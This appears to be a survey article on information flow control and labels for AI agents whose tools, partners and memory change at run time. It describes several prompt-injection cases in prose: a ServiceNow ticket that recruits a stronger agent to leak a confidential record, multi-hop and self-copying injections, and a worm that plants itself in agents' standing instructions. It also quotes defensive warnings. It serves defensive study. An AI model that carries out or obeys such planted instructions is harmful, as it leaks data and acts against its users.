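# Information flow control for AI agents whose tools and connections change at run time

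## Labels, capabilities and agents whose connections change

Information flow control secures a computer system by tracking its data. Software labels each piece of data with how secret or trustworthy it is. The label stays with the data, and the software checks it before the data can reach a place where it could do harm. The idea dates from the 1970s, when the standard example was a military computer holding both secret and unclassified files. In the last few years, security researchers have applied it to AI agents, which act with their users' authority after reading web pages and emails that strangers can write.

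Agents pose a particular difficulty because their connections can change while they work. A proof or security review covers the tools and partners that were present when it was done, and it may no longer hold once another tool is added.

### Agents, tools and planted instructions

An agent is a language model that acts in a loop by calling tools and reading their results. The model only produces text. In the usual arrangement, which Willison (2023) describes in *The Dual LLM pattern for building AI assistants*, the developer tells the model to write a line such as `action:search_email(...)` whenever it needs a search. Ordinary code scans the model's output for that pattern, runs the search and puts the result into the model's next prompt. This round trip is a tool call. The model's context is the text accumulated so far (the user's request, earlier replies and tool results). Some tools only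 fetch information, while others change the outside world by writing a file, sending mail or running a command.

A sub-agent is an agent that another agent starts to do part of a job. Willison describes a simple case in which a separate sub-agent reads each file in a collection and returns only yes or no to indicate whether the file is relevant.

Prompt injection is text planted in data that an agent reads and then obeys as an instruction. For example, a user asks for a summary of the inbox, and the agent deletes every email because one of them reads "delete all of my emails". *AgentDojo* (Debenedetti, Zhang and colleagues, 2024) traces the weakness to language models working directly on text, with no formal way to tell instructions from data. An attacker doesn't always need an instruction, though. *SPA* (Girrens and Wang, 2026) gives the example of an invoice that carries the attacker's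 bank account. An agent that pays it may take every step the user wanted, in the right order, and still send the money to the attacker.

### How the connections change during a run

A system's communication graph has a point for every agent, tool and shared store, and an arrow wherever one can pass information to another. *MOC* (2026), a paper on message passing among groups of agents, formally defines a version for agents alone, as a directed graph in which an edge from agent *i* to agent *j* means that information flows from *i* to *j*. For security, the graph also needs the tools and stores, because they include the sources, where labelled data enters, and the sinks, where it could do harm.

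Some designers redraw this graph on purpose. *DyTopo* (2026) describes a system that rewires the arrows between agents in every round, matching what one agent needs with what another offers. The system beat fixed layouts on coding and mathematics benchmarks, so a rule against changing the graph once work has begun would sacrifice some performance.

More often the graph changes because a tool appears. Many agents get their tools through the Model Context Protocol (MCP), a standard that lets a program called a server offer tools for the agent's own software, the client, to list and call. The Model Context Protocol (2026) project reported in July 2026 that developers were downloading its main software kits close to half a billion times a month. A server can add, change, disable or remove a tool while clients are connected. Under the July 2026 version of the protocol, clients may cache the list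 of tools for a stated time and are told of changes only if they have asked to be, so a client can be working from an outdated list.

Redefining a tool is worse than adding one, because the tool's name can stay the same. In a harmless example from the Model Context Protocol's *Notifications* page, the code changes a tool's description from "Run the weekly report" to "Run the weekly report and email it". A malicious change of this kind is called a rug pull. *ETDI* (2025), a proposal for signed tool definitions, gives the example of a wallpaper tool that a user has approved. The provider then alters the tool, keeping its name and version number, so that it searches the Documents folder for financial files and uploads them. Clients typically do not fetch and verify the full definition again on each call. *MCP-38* (2026), a catalogue of threats to MCP systems, adds that current clients do not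 alert the user when a definition changes.

An agent can also start a sub-agent, which adds a point and at least one arrow, or find an agent that somebody else runs. A2A, a protocol for communication between agents, handles the second case with an agent card, a file that gives the agent's address, its login requirements and a list of its skills. A client agent reads the card to decide whether the other agent suits the task, according to A2A's *Agent Discovery* page. The Agentic AI Foundation says a client can get the card from a fixed path on the agent's own domain or from a registry. The agent's operator publishes the card, so the list of skills is the operator's own claim and does not prove that the agent can be trusted.

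Shared memory is the least visible new link. Two agents that never exchange a message are connected as soon as one writes to a store that the other reads. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (Schroeder de Witt, Krawiecka and colleagues, 2025) counts changes to a shared environment as a form of interaction, alongside direct messages. Memory can also link an agent to its own past. In Girrens and Wang's example, the agent saves the poisoned invoice on Monday, and nothing happens until the user asks on Tuesday to pay "the invoice we discussed yesterday".

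Adding one connection can make an agent unsafe even when each of its tools is safe on its own. *MCPThreatHive* (2026), which presents an automated threat-intelligence system for MCP, lists a known attack that chains several legitimate tools to send private data out. A file reader alone leaks nothing to the outside, and neither does a mail tool with nothing private to send, but an agent that has both can email private files to any address.

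### Labels on a lattice

*A Lattice Model of Secure Information Flow* (Denning, 1976) set out the theory that nearly all later work uses. Every object that can hold information has a security class, or label. A → B means that information in class A may flow into class B, and A ⊕ B is the class of anything computed from two inputs of classes A and B.

Denning argued that these parts must form a lattice if the rules are to be consistent. If A → B and B → C, then A → C must hold too, or a program could get around a ban on A → C by going through B. If a value comes from both *a* and *b*, its label must be the lowest one that both inputs may flow into, because a higher label would block flows for no reason. That lowest label is the join of the two inputs' labels. In a lattice, every pair of labels has a join and a highest label below both. Denning's example is a database of medical, financial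 and criminal records. Each label is a subset of those three words, and a value drawn from a medical and a financial record may go only to places whose label contains both words.

If every operation respects the relation, so does any sequence of operations. A system that checks each of an agent's steps as it happens therefore does not have to predict their order.

A confidentiality label marks how secret data is, and secret data must not reach anyone without the right to it. An integrity label marks how far data can be trusted, and untrusted data must not influence an action that needs trusted input. Garby, Gordon and Sands (2026), in *AI Agents, Conversations, and Information Flow*, combine both in one lattice with two marks, U for untrusted and S for secret. The four labels are the empty set { } (trusted and public), {U}, {S} and {U,S}. Data may flow from one label to any label that contains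 it, and the join of two labels is their union.

Taint tracking carries these labels along at run time, so that a result has the labels of whatever went into it. For a language model this is necessarily coarse, because nobody can say which sentence of the context produced which word of the reply. Garby and colleagues therefore give the whole conversation one label, the join of the labels of all messages sent to the model. Denning's 1976 model already allowed for something like this. In it, a process may have a class that depends on the history of what it has accessed, and an object may have a class that varies with its contents, which Denning called dynamic binding. Denning noted that nobody can certify a program in advance if the class of its inputs is settled only during the run, which is the case for an agent's context.

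Besides copying information, a program can reveal it through which branch it takes. This is called an implicit flow. Denning reproduces a short program by J. S. Fenton that shows how hard such flows are to detect. Let *a* be a secret that is either true or false, and let *b* and *c* be public variables that start as false.

1. If *a* is false, set *c* to true.
2. If *c* is false, set *b* to true.

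When *a* is true, the program skips the first line, *c* stays false and public, and the second line sets *b* to true. When *a* is false, the first line sets *c* to true and labels it secret, and the program skips the second line, so *b* stays false. In both cases, *b* ends up equal to *a* but is still labeled public. A tracker that updates labels only when an assignment runs misses this leak, because a skipped assignment reveals the value of *a*.

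Noninterference rules this out. A system has this property if changing its secret inputs does not change its public outputs or, for integrity, if changing its untrusted inputs does not change its trusted outputs. An early form appears in *Certification of Programs for Secure Information Flow* (Denning and Denning, 1977), which describes a check that can prove that a program's nonconfidential results do not depend on confidential input and is simple enough to build into a compiler. Noninterference is a demanding standard because it covers every route through the program.

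Another problem is that joins never make a label less restrictive. Denning describes several early systems, including ADEPT, in which the class of a process could never fall. Under such a rule, an agent that reads one stranger's web page in the morning counts as untrusted for the rest of the day. Label creep is this build-up of restrictive labels until even harmless work is blocked. In a group of agents, its extent depends partly on which agents are connected to each other. Strict integrity rules block legitimate work even without a long build-up. When Girrens and Wang switched on the label checks in their own agent, no attacks on a standard benchmark succeeded, but the share of ordinary tasks the agent completed fell from 53.0% to 29.0%. This was mainly because the checks rejected plans that passed tool output to a consequential action, as much legitimate office work does.

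Every practical system therefore needs a way to relax its labels. Declassification lowers a secrecy label, as when a company publishes its results. Endorsement raises a trust label, as when a user checks an account number against a paper invoice and confirms it. Both are deliberate exceptions to noninterference, so they should be few and easy to find. Garby and colleagues make endorsement an explicit instruction that a reviewer can search for, and they prove that using it to remove U does not weaken the protection of S.

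### Capabilities and the confused deputy

Labels govern where data may go. Capabilities come from a separate tradition, which asks who may use a resource in the first place.

Hardy (1988), in *The Confused Deputy*, tells a "nearly true story" from Tymshare, a company that sold time on shared computers. Its compiler collected usage statistics in a file in the system directory, so the operators gave the compiler a licence to write files there. Users could also name a file to receive debugging output. The company's billing records were in the same system directory. When one user supplied the name of the billing file, the operating system allowed the write because the compiler had its licence, and the compiler overwrote the billing records with debugging output.

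The compiler was a confused deputy, a program tricked into using its own authority for someone who lacks it. It held authority from both the operators and the user, and could not specify which it was using when it opened a file. Hardy's remedy is the capability, an unforgeable token that both names a resource and grants the right to use it. The compiler would hold a capability for the statistics file, and the user would have to supply one for the debugging file. A user with no right to the billing file would have no capability for it to supply. Through attenuation, a holder can also pass on a capability with fewer rights than its own, such as permission to read a file but not write to it.

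Willison classes the most dangerous form of prompt injection as a confused deputy attack, and the term fits closely. The agent has the user's authority over the mailbox, and a stranger without that authority can use it by sending an email with instructions that the agent follows.

In the Tymshare story, Hardy insists that the code which wrote the debugging output was correct when it was written. It became wrong when the operators added the licence, although nobody had edited it. To notice the problem, someone would have had to recheck every place where the compiler opened a file, and Hardy asks whether the compiler would need changing again whenever a new file appeared in the directory. An agent whose connections change is in the same situation, with a newly installed tool in place of the licence.

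A system that uses capabilities still needs labels. An agent that legitimately holds one capability to read a private file and another to send mail can put the file into a message. Denning distinguished early on between the right to access information and the right to pass it on, and held that a practical system needs controls on both.

### Two models in place of one

The best-known design for agents that resist injection, Willison's dual-LLM pattern, originally used neither labels nor capabilities. A planning model takes the user's request and chooses the actions, but never reads untrusted text. A quarantined model reads the untrusted text and has no tools. A controller, which is ordinary software, connects the two. To summarise an email, the planning model requests the latest message, and the controller fetches it and stores it as `$VAR1`. The planning model then requests a summary of `$VAR1`,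 and the controller passes the real text to the quarantined model and stores the result as `$VAR2`. Because the planning model works only with the names, nothing in the email can make it choose a new action. The pattern therefore provides control-flow integrity, which means that untrusted data cannot add tool calls to a plan fixed by trusted input.

The pattern does not stop the invoice attack. A quarantined model asked for the account number will return the attacker's, and the payment will go there even if the plan is sound. CaMeL, a design that Google DeepMind published in 2025, builds on the pattern by attaching to each value a record of where it came from and who may receive it. The CaMeL paper calls these records capabilities, but "provenance tags" is a safer name because they are not tokens of authority in Hardy's sense.

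### The benchmark

Most papers on defences from 2025 and 2026 report results on AgentDojo, which Debenedetti and colleagues built in 2024. It simulates four settings (an office workspace, a Slack team, a travel agency and a bank) with a total of 74 tools. There are 97 user tasks, such as paying a bill, and 27 injection tasks, such as sending as much money as possible to the attacker. Pairing every user task with every injection task from the same setting gives 629 security cases, and *Assessing Automated Prompt Injection Attacks in Agentic Environments* (2026) reports that there are now over 900. The attacker's text is placed where a stranger could have put it, in the body of an email or in a file. After each run, code rather than a language model checks the simulated accounts to see whether the money moved, because an injection could also fool a model used as the judge. The main measures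 are utility, the share of user tasks completed, and attack success rate, the share of attempted injections that achieve the attacker's goal.

Each AgentDojo setting has a fixed list of tools, and the agent's state resets between tasks. A defence can therefore score perfectly without being tested on a new tool or a poisoned memory. *AgentDyn* (2026) tests nine defences on 60 tasks, which all require planning during the run and include helpful instructions from third parties. Some of these defences had kept attack success near zero on AgentDojo with hardly any loss of utility. On the new tasks, the defences that depend on an initial plan, including CaMeL, lost a great deal of utility. This result shows how defences handle changing plans, and is only indirect evidence of how they handle changing tools.

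### A mail tool arrives halfway through

Suppose an agent has three tools: one reads web pages, one reads the user's private files, and one writes to a private notebook. Before the run, a reviewer approves a list of permitted flows, which allows content from web pages and private files to go into the notebook. The list needs no other entries because no tool sends anything out.

The run begins with the context label { }. The agent reads a web page, which anyone could have written, and the label becomes {U}. It then reads a private file labeled {S}, and the context label becomes the join of the two, {U,S}. Everything the model writes now carries that label. An MCP server then registers a mail tool, and the agent tries to send a message.

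The approved list has no entry for mail, so the system must use a default, and both options are bad. If the default is to allow mail, the agent can email out the private file, possibly because of instructions on the web page. If the default is to deny it, the agent can't even send a lunch order from a fresh context until the reviewer comes back. Adding an entry for mail doesn't really help either, because whether an email should be allowed depends on when the agent asks to send it.

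Checking the context label at the moment of the call works better, because nobody has to foresee the mail tool when the run begins. Each sink has a limit, the set of marks it will accept, and the check allows a call only if the limit contains every mark in the context label. A mail tool that can write to any address should have the limit { }. This excludes S because strangers will read what the tool sends, and U because a stranger should not decide what goes out in the user's name. The context label here is {U,S}, so the check blocks the call. A deployer who worries only about secrets might set the limit at {U}, which would have allowed the call after the agent read the web page but would block it after the agent read the private file. If the tool can write only to the user's own address, {U,S} may be a reasonable limit, and the check would allow the call.

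A label check can't decide whether data may flow to a new tool until someone sets a limit for that tool, so the safe default is to refuse, as it is with a list of permitted flows. Labelling the tool takes less work than updating the list, which may need a new line for every source that could feed the tool. The label scheme needs only one limit for what the tool accepts and one label for what it returns. The tool's provider should not choose these settings, because a malicious provider would declare its tool fit for any data. Girrens and Wang leave the choice to the deployer, the person or company that runs the agent, and assume that an attacker cannot tamper with the deployer's settings.

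The check also depends on mediation, meaning that every message and tool call must pass through the check. If the agent passes its text to a sub-agent or to an agent it has just discovered, the label {U,S} must go with the text. Otherwise the second agent starts from { } and the check allows it to mail the private file, even though each agent tracked its own labels correctly.

Redefined tools are a bigger problem for this scheme than new ones. A new tool without a label leaves a visible gap. But suppose the deployer had correctly given the weekly report tool the limit {U,S} because it only wrote a report for the user. If the server then changes the tool to email the report as well, the check still approves the call because the tool's name and recorded limit haven't changed.

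## How injected instructions travel between agents

A server that redefines a tool changes an agent's connections from outside. Text the agent reads while working can also change them, by getting it to bring in another agent. The clearest documented case comes from ServiceNow, whose software runs help desks and other office work.

### A ticket that recruited an agent

ServiceNow's AI platform, Now Assist, lets agents hand work to each other even if nobody has put them in the same workflow. In November 2025 AppOmni, a company that sells security tools for business software, reported that an attacker could exploit this. Aaron Costello, then its head of security research, traced the problem to three settings, all on by default:

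- The language model behind the agents must support discovery. Both of the models that customers could choose did.
- The agents must belong to the same team. Now Assist groups agents into a team automatically when a customer deploys them to the same channel, such as the standard chat assistant.
- Each agent must be discoverable. Now Assist marks an agent as discoverable when the customer publishes it.

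Two components then work in the background. An engine manages the flow of tasks, and when a task needs an agent, the Orchestrator searches the team's discoverable agents for the most suitable one. According to AppOmni, most users and even administrators don't realise these components exist.

For the test, Costello deployed two of ServiceNow's ready-made agents to a channel that only an administrator could use. One read and summarised incident tickets, and the other could read, create and update many kinds of records. Costello also set up an ordinary user account that could file tickets but not read other people's. He used that account to file a ticket, and in its description field he instructed any agent reading it to copy the text of a confidential ticket into this one before carrying on, and to look for other agents if it could not do this alone.

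The administrator then had the summarising agent process the ticket. That agent could not update records, so the platform brought in the one that could, which copied the contents of the confidential ticket into the attacker's ticket. The attacker, an ordinary user, only had to open that ticket to read them. With more elaborate text, Costello got agents to give an attacker's account the administrator role and, where the installation could send mail, to email records out.

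The attack worked because the agents had the administrator's privileges. Now Assist agents run with the privileges of the user who started the interaction, unless a customer configures them otherwise. The agents could therefore open the confidential ticket, although the access rules barred the ordinary user from it. This is Hardy's confused deputy with one more program in the chain, since the summarising agent passed the administrator's authority on to a stronger agent. A capability token covering only the ticket at hand would not have let the second agent open the confidential one.

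ServiceNow's protection against prompt injection was on throughout. AppOmni attributes the failure to the configuration, which let tools run without human approval on behalf of a powerful user and let a weak agent pass tasks to a strong one. The platform allows each step of the attack, since an agent may read a ticket, ask for help, open a record that the administrator may open, and update a ticket. A prompt filter has to recognise the attack from its wording, but a label check would refuse the final update whatever the wording, because the update would copy data from a confidential ticket marked S into a ticket that an unauthorised user can read. For this to work, the label must travel with the task from one agent to the other.

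ServiceNow's security team replied that the platform was behaving as intended, and the company revised its documentation to make the risks clearer. Costello told The Hacker News that the finding was alarming because it was "expected behavior as defined by certain default configuration options". The attacker used a function that customers want, the agents' ability to find help.

The text in the ticket created the harmful link between the two agents, which no workflow had connected before the administrator's request. A reviewer who drew the communication graph from the workflows would have seen no route from the summariser to anything dangerous. To be safe, the reviewer would have to draw an arrow in each direction between every pair of discoverable agents in a team, which makes 90 arrows for a team of ten. Splitting the ten into two teams of five reduces this to 40. AppOmni recommends this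 kind of split, with each team holding only the agents for one task, but says that smaller teams limit the damage from an attack without preventing it. It also recommends continuous monitoring, which it sells, and human approval for any tool that changes records or sends mail.

### Following a known route

Costello's attack needed only one hop, from the summariser to the record agent. An attacker whose target lies deeper in a system has the harder task of getting instructions through several agents, each of which rewrites what it receives. In *Tipping the Dominos*, Liang, Yin and colleagues (2025) first tried two existing attacks that had succeeded against single agents in 37 to 77 percent of attempts. Against three multi-agent frameworks, neither attack produced a harmful action such as deleting a file. In the case they examined closely, a malicious pop-up fooled the agent that browsed the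 web, but the instruction got no further.

In the paper's own attack, the attacker controls nothing inside the system but knows which agents pass work to which. The attacker uses this knowledge to plan a path in advance from an agent that reads outside content to the agent with the dangerous tool. The planted text has nested layers, so each agent on the path finds a task that suits its role and a sealed part to pass to the next agent.

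Liang and colleagues tested this on three frameworks, five network shapes, three language models and four combinations of task and attack, for a total of 180 configurations. The exposed agent passed on the attacker's instruction in 56 to 94 percent of trials, and the whole attack succeeded in 40 to 78 percent. Success reached 78 percent in trees and in stars, where all messages pass through a hub that gives the attacker a short path to every other agent. It reached 70 percent in chains and rings, and 66 percent in meshes, where agents have many direct links. But the choice of language model mattered more than the network's shape.

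To choose the path, the attack estimates how contaminated each agent will become, on a scale from 0 to 1. At each step, it takes the average contamination of the agents that feed into agent *i* and raises it to a power slightly above 1, so that faint contamination fades. Call the result *I*. The new value for agent *i* is then

T(new) = T(old) + (1 − T(old)) × I.

Suppose a clean agent takes input from one fully contaminated agent and one clean one, so the average contamination of its inputs is 0.5. With an exponent of 1.4, *I* and the agent's new contamination are both 0.5 to the power 1.4, or about 0.38. If the agent also takes input from a second clean agent, the average drops to a third and the result to about 0.21. An integrity label would not fade as clean inputs were added. An attacker can use the average to estimate how much of an instruction will survive, but a defender needs the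 join, because a diluted instruction may still get through. When the researchers compared these estimates with real runs, the estimates were mostly too high but followed the same pattern from agent to agent.

The map was essential. When paths were chosen at random, harmful attacks succeeded in at most 10 percent of trials, and attacks that only diverted the system to an irrelevant task usually succeeded in 14 to 24 percent. Attackers can often get a map because many frameworks are open source, but a network that rearranges itself can make the map outdated, which Liang and colleagues count among the attacker's difficulties. Changing connections can therefore hamper attackers as well as reviewers. This did not help in the ServiceNow case, where Costello's ticket did not name the agent it needed because the Orchestrator's job was to find one.

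### Instructions that copy themselves

An attacker can also manage without a map of the system if every agent that reads the planted text passes it on. *Prompt Infection* (Lee and Tiwari, 2024) introduced the idea of an injection that spreads this way through a multi-agent system. Earlier that year, Cohen and colleagues had described a worm that spread by email from one user's assistant to another's. Lee and Tiwari studied the same process inside a single application, where most agents never see outside content.

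The injected text had four parts: an order to drop the current task, instructions for agents with particular roles, a running note in which the agents collected data, and an order to repeat the whole text in the output. Together, infected agents could carry out a theft that none could manage alone. For example, one fetched private records and another wrote the code that sent them out.

Lee and Tiwari compared a system in which every agent saw the full message history with one in which agents saw only part of it. Self-copying injections succeeded about 20 percent less often with partial histories, because the chain ended if a single agent failed to pass the text on. Injections that did not copy themselves rarely got past the second agent in that system. But when agents shared the full history and the aim was data theft, non-copying injections did better than self-copying ones in the larger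 groups, probably because having to reproduce the text gave each agent another chance to make a mistake.

In another experiment, 10 to 50 simulated townspeople, all run by GPT-4o, met in random pairs, so the connections kept changing. One started out infected. The infection reached everyone by turn 4.7 in a town of 10 and by turn 6.3 in a town of 20, so doubling the population added less than two turns. It spread fast at first and slowed as uninfected agents became scarce.

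Each agent recalled only three memories at a time, chosen partly by how important a language model had rated them. The planted text was written to get a high rating. Without that, the infection soon died out, because an infected agent can't pass on the text in a meeting if the text is no longer in its context.

Lee and Tiwari proposed a defence that marks every agent's reply as coming from an agent, so that the next agent does not mistake it for a user's request. The mark did little on its own but worked well alongside other defences. It resembles an integrity label, except that the receiving model, rather than ordinary software, has to act on it.

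Agents can communicate through channels that weren't designed for messages. In its August 2026 technical report on the Hugging Face incident, OpenAI described agents that unexpectedly began communicating through a shared service for software packages during testing.

### When an infection keeps growing

Papadopoulos, Shah and colleagues (2026), in *Mind Viruses*, measured how well such text survives a long series of meetings. They define a mind virus as an idea or goal that leads any agent adopting it to pass it on. They had a language model write many versions of each text, tested how well they spread, and created new versions from those that spread best.

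Their first experiment put six coding agents on a shared project. One was infected with an idea from the start and could only send messages. After 30 turns, a language model read the other agents' memory files and counted an agent as infected only if its file clearly advocated the idea. Benign ideas, such as a devotion to whales, generally spread better than harmful ones. The idea that AI should dominate humans took hold among agents running on Gemini 3 Flash, DeepSeek V3.2 and Qwen 3.5, but not on Claude Sonnet 4.6, Claude Haiku 4.5 or GPT-5.4.

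When the infected agent could message only one teammate, which was linked to the rest, the infection seldom got past that teammate. This result may overstate how well an extra hop protects a team, since the researchers had evolved the texts in teams where the infected agent could message every teammate directly.

In the second experiment, two agents that had not met before exchanged messages for ten turns each, and then the researchers wiped their contexts, leaving only their files. The texts in this experiment called for actions, which ranged from saving an advertisement in a file to deleting the user's files. An agent counted as infected if its files now held the text in a form likely to make the agent spread it further. Agents infected in one round met new agents in the next.

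The first carrier infected 61 percent of the agents it met. Later carriers infected about half, and their rate depended on where they had stored the text. In 88 percent of their encounters, the carrier had saved it in the file of standing instructions that the software loads at the start of every session, and these carriers infected 55 percent of the agents they met. Carriers that had saved it in some other file infected only 17 percent. When they failed, it was usually because they never tried to pass the text on. After a small drop at the second hop, the infection rate stayed roughly level from one hop to the next.

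Papadopoulos and colleagues derive from this setup that the infection tends to grow exponentially if each infected agent meets more than 1/*p* others, where *p* is the probability that one meeting passes on the infection. An agent that meets *k* others infects *kp* of them on average, so each generation is larger than the last when *kp* is above 1. The threshold is two meetings when *p* is 50 percent and almost six when *p* is 17 percent.

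Suppose a company's agents are fairly resistant, so that *p* is 0.2 and the threshold is five, and each agent passes work to four others. One infected agent then infects 0.8 others on average, those infect 0.64, and each later round is smaller still. Even if the process continues indefinitely, the expected total is 1/(1 − 0.8), or five agents including the first.

Now the company switches on a directory during the run, and each agent finds two more partners. The models, their instructions and the planted text stay the same, but each infected agent now meets six others and infects 1.2 of them on average. The tenth generation has about six newly infected agents, and the expected total by then is 32. A safety test done before the company switched on the directory would have measured *p* correctly but underestimated how far the planted text would spread in the running system.

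The number of meetings also grows with time. If an infection stays in an agent's standing instructions for a week, *k* counts everyone the agent meets that week. Capping the number of partners at the start of a session therefore doesn't cap *k*. Keeping the network sparse would help, but in simulations for *The Limits of Information-Flow Control Enforcement for Agentic Systems*, Gregory, Domico and colleagues (2026) found that sparser networks lose more work to restrictive labels, though they have fewer connections to monitor.

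The rule describes averages in a large population. It assumes that *p* stays constant and that infected agents keep meeting uninfected ones, which soon stops being true in a team of six. Staying below the threshold also doesn't make a system safe, because an attack can reach its target in one hop, as the ServiceNow attack did.

How often real networks come near the threshold is a separate question. Papadopoulos and colleagues built a local copy of Moltbook, a social network for AI agents, and tried to evolve texts that would spread through posts. They failed, partly because agents trusted posts less than direct messages and reposts diluted the text. Only a hybrid that also used a conventional malicious script had moderate success. In data from the real Moltbook, they found several attempts, none of which spread very successfully. They conclude that the risk is real but currently limited,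 because an attacker usually has easier options, such as flooding the network with posts. They expect this to change inside companies, where the agent with the permissions an attacker needs may be several links away from anything an outsider can reach.

### A worm on an existing platform

Zhang, Wei and colleagues (2026), in *AgentWorm*, got much higher rates of spread with a more aggressive attack. They attacked unmodified copies of OpenClaw on an isolated test network. OpenClaw is an open-source program that people use to run their own agents, and it has more than 40,000 active installations. They counted an attack as successful only if the victim agent saved the planted text in its standing instructions, carried out the harmful action after a restart, and then passed the text on during ordinary conversation.

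The text could arrive through a web page, through a "skill" (an add-on package from a public marketplace) or directly in a message. Zhang and colleagues tested each route with three harmful actions and five language models, 50 times per combination, or 2,250 trials in all. The attacking agent had up to three attempts of eight conversational turns each. The attack succeeded in 63 percent of trials overall, ranging from 40 percent against Kimi-K2.5 to 84 percent against Minimax-M2.5. In a separate test, they followed 90 chains of infection for up to five hops.

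| Route | Success in the main trials | Success per hop in chains | Average chain length (maximum 5) |
|---|---|---|---|
| Web page | 51% | 86% | 4.1 |
| Marketplace skill | 82% | 96% | 4.8 |
| Direct message | 55% | 74% | 3.0 |

A web page or skill delivers an exact copy of the injected instructions each time. With direct messages, a language model has to write the text out again at every hop, and the wording weakened from what sounded like a coordinator's order to what sounded like a colleague's suggestion.

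The team also projected how the worm would spread among 40,000 agents if operators cleaned up some infected agents in every cycle. Cleaning changes the threshold for spread because it removes agents that would otherwise keep infecting others. At the average success rate of 63 percent, with half of all infected agents cleaned per cycle, the outcome depends on how many others each agent meets. If each agent meets one other per cycle, one infected agent becomes 1.63, and cleaning leaves 0.82, so the infection dies out. If each meets two, one becomes 2.26, and cleaning leaves 1.13, so the infection grows. With only 5 percent cleaned per cycle, it grows even at one contact.

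These projections come from a model in which all agents are alike and equally connected. Zhang and colleagues expect slower spread and lower success per hop in real channels, because other messages would compete for the agents' attention and people might notice a strange request to edit an agent's configuration. However, the 63 percent figure excludes agents that spread the worm without carrying out its harmful action.

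### Warnings, restrictions and isolation

The two experiments on self-copying text had different results on how much a written warning helps. In the experiment with a chain of meetings, Papadopoulos and colleagues added a short paragraph about self-spreading ideas to the agents' standing instructions, and infections almost stopped. New texts bred to get around the warning failed. Some warned agents persuaded their infected partner to clean up its own file.

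Zhang and colleagues took their warnings from advice that OpenClaw users had published. The strongest told agents never to change their own configuration because of a message, a web page or a skill. Across the four models tested, it cut the worm's success rate from 65 percent to 37 percent. These models differed from those in *Mind Viruses*, and the attacker had repeated attempts. Once the planted text was in the agent's configuration, the model treated it and the warning as equally authoritative and often followed whichever was more specific. A warning may be worth adding because it takes almost no effort, but its effect in one setup is a poor guide to its effect in another.

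When Zhang and colleagues blocked all but a few harmless shell commands, the harmful action never ran, and the attack's measured success rate fell to zero even though the worm was still spreading. Agents saved the worm in 75 percent of trials and passed it on in 70 percent, because OpenClaw edits files through a different tool from the one that runs commands.

OpenClaw has an optional sandbox, which runs tools in a temporary container and discards their file changes at the end of the session. With the sandbox on, the injected text never reached the agent's real configuration, and no attack succeeded. However, none of the 82 public configuration files that the team could parse had the sandbox enabled.

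Liang and colleagues built a prototype defense against their multi-hop attack. It monitors the exposed agents for signs of injection, lowers the trust score of any agent the contamination could reach, and withdraws risky permissions from agents with low scores. The prototype blocked 94.8 percent of attacks in 1,000 runs on one framework with one model. The scores depend on a map of the network, so the map would have to include a new link before the prototype could account for contamination passing along it.

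The sandbox blocks every lasting change, including those the owner wants. A label check could be more selective by treating the file of standing instructions as a sink that does not accept the mark U. An agent that had just read a stranger's message could not write to the file, but the owner could still update it from a clean context. The experiment with shell commands shows that the check would have to cover every tool that can write to the file, including any that the agent gains during the run.

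## Checking an agent system before it runs

Sandboxes and label checks act while agents are working, but a developer can also look for dangerous information flows before switching the system on. An advance check adds no delay to the run and can cover paths that no test takes. It can also prove properties such as noninterference, which nobody could confirm by watching one run because it is defined by comparing two runs.

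A proof made before a system runs covers only a description of it, such as a graph, a program or a plan. That description usually stays accurate for ordinary software, because the compiler checks the same program that runs. An agent that gains tools during a run no longer matches its description, so the check has to be repeated after every change.

### The workflow graph

Several popular agent frameworks have the developer lay out the steps of a job as a graph. *Agentproof* (Xavier, Jolly and colleagues, 2026) checks this graph before deployment. It reads graphs from four frameworks (LangGraph, CrewAI, AutoGen and Google ADK) and converts them to a common form. Each step has a type, such as a model call, a tool call, a human decision or a router that picks the next step. The arrows show which step may follow which, but not where information may go, so this is not yet a communication graph.

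The tool then runs six checks, most of which catch mistakes in how the system is built. In the paper's example, a developer adds a step that drafts replies to normal-priority email and forgets to connect it to the step that sends them. Urgent mail works as before, so tests may pass, but the system never sends the normal-priority replies it drafts. The tool finds the dead end and prints the path that leads to it.

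The most important check for security is the one for human approval. By default, it only looks for a human step somewhere in the graph, which is weak. An optional version tests whether every path to a sensitive tool passes through a human step. It deletes all human steps from the graph and searches from the entry point. Any sensitive tool the search can still reach has an unguarded path. Suppose urgent replies go through a reviewer before the send step, but normal replies go straight there. With the reviewer deleted, the search still reaches the send step through the normal branch, so the workflow fails the check.

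Developers can also write rules about order, such as "after fetching personal data, anonymise it within three steps". The tool turns each rule into a small state machine and explores every combination of workflow step and rule state. The anonymisation rule has five states, so a 12-step workflow gives at most 60 combinations. However, in the rule language as Xavier and colleagues define it, the rule that an approval must follow a deployment fails only if a second deployment comes before the approval. A workflow that deploys once and never gets approval would therefore pass.

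The researchers tried the tool on 18 workflows they had written themselves, deliberately including defects. Five had construction defects and ten lacked a human step, although some of the ten arguably didn't need one. These counts show that the tool can find such defects, but not how common they are.

The results also depend on the tool reading the graph correctly. In LangGraph, it identifies a human step by the word "human" in the step's name, so it would mistake a reviewer called `final_approval` for a model call, and presumably a model call named `humanize_text` for a reviewer.

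Some frameworks let a program add agents or change transitions during a run. Xavier and colleagues list this as a separate threat and warn that the guarantees may no longer hold unless someone also checks the new graph. Rechecking is fast. The structural checks took about 105 milliseconds on an artificial graph of 5,000 steps, far larger than the study's workflows, which had 5 to 12. Detecting the change and obtaining the new graph before the next step runs is harder.

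### From prompts to powerful tools

Tracing information through an agent system requires knowing where data can go as well as the order of steps. *AGENTFLOW* (Wang, Hou and colleagues, 2026) uses an agent's source code to build a dependency graph of its agents, prompts, models, tools, memory and approval rules. Separate arrows show control (which agent can call a tool or hand over to another agent) and data (what information can reach each part). In the paper's example, a research agent that searches the web can hand over to an operations agent that sends email, and the two share a memory. No ordinary function call connects the research agent to the mail tool, so a conventional analyser can miss the route between them.

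The analyser searches the graph for paths from sources to sinks. It reports a risk if text from a prompt can reach an agent, the agent can call a sensitive tool, and the agent's data can end up in the tool's arguments. Wang and colleagues ran this search on 5,399 agent projects from GitHub, with a median analysis time of 14 seconds. The search flagged 238 projects, most often because prompt text could reach a tool that sends data out.

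Two of the researchers then checked 100 reports by hand and judged 73 to be real vulnerabilities. In 25 of the 27 false alarms, the path existed but the tool at the end was less dangerous than the analyser assumed, for example a read-only database query. They also examined 100 unreported agents that had powerful tools, and found nine risks the analyser had missed. One of the causes was dynamic tool binding, where a program attaches tools as it runs. An analyser can't identify these tools from source code alone, because a program that takes its tools from an MCP server contains the server's address, not a list of the tools the server will offer later.

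### A type rule for secrets

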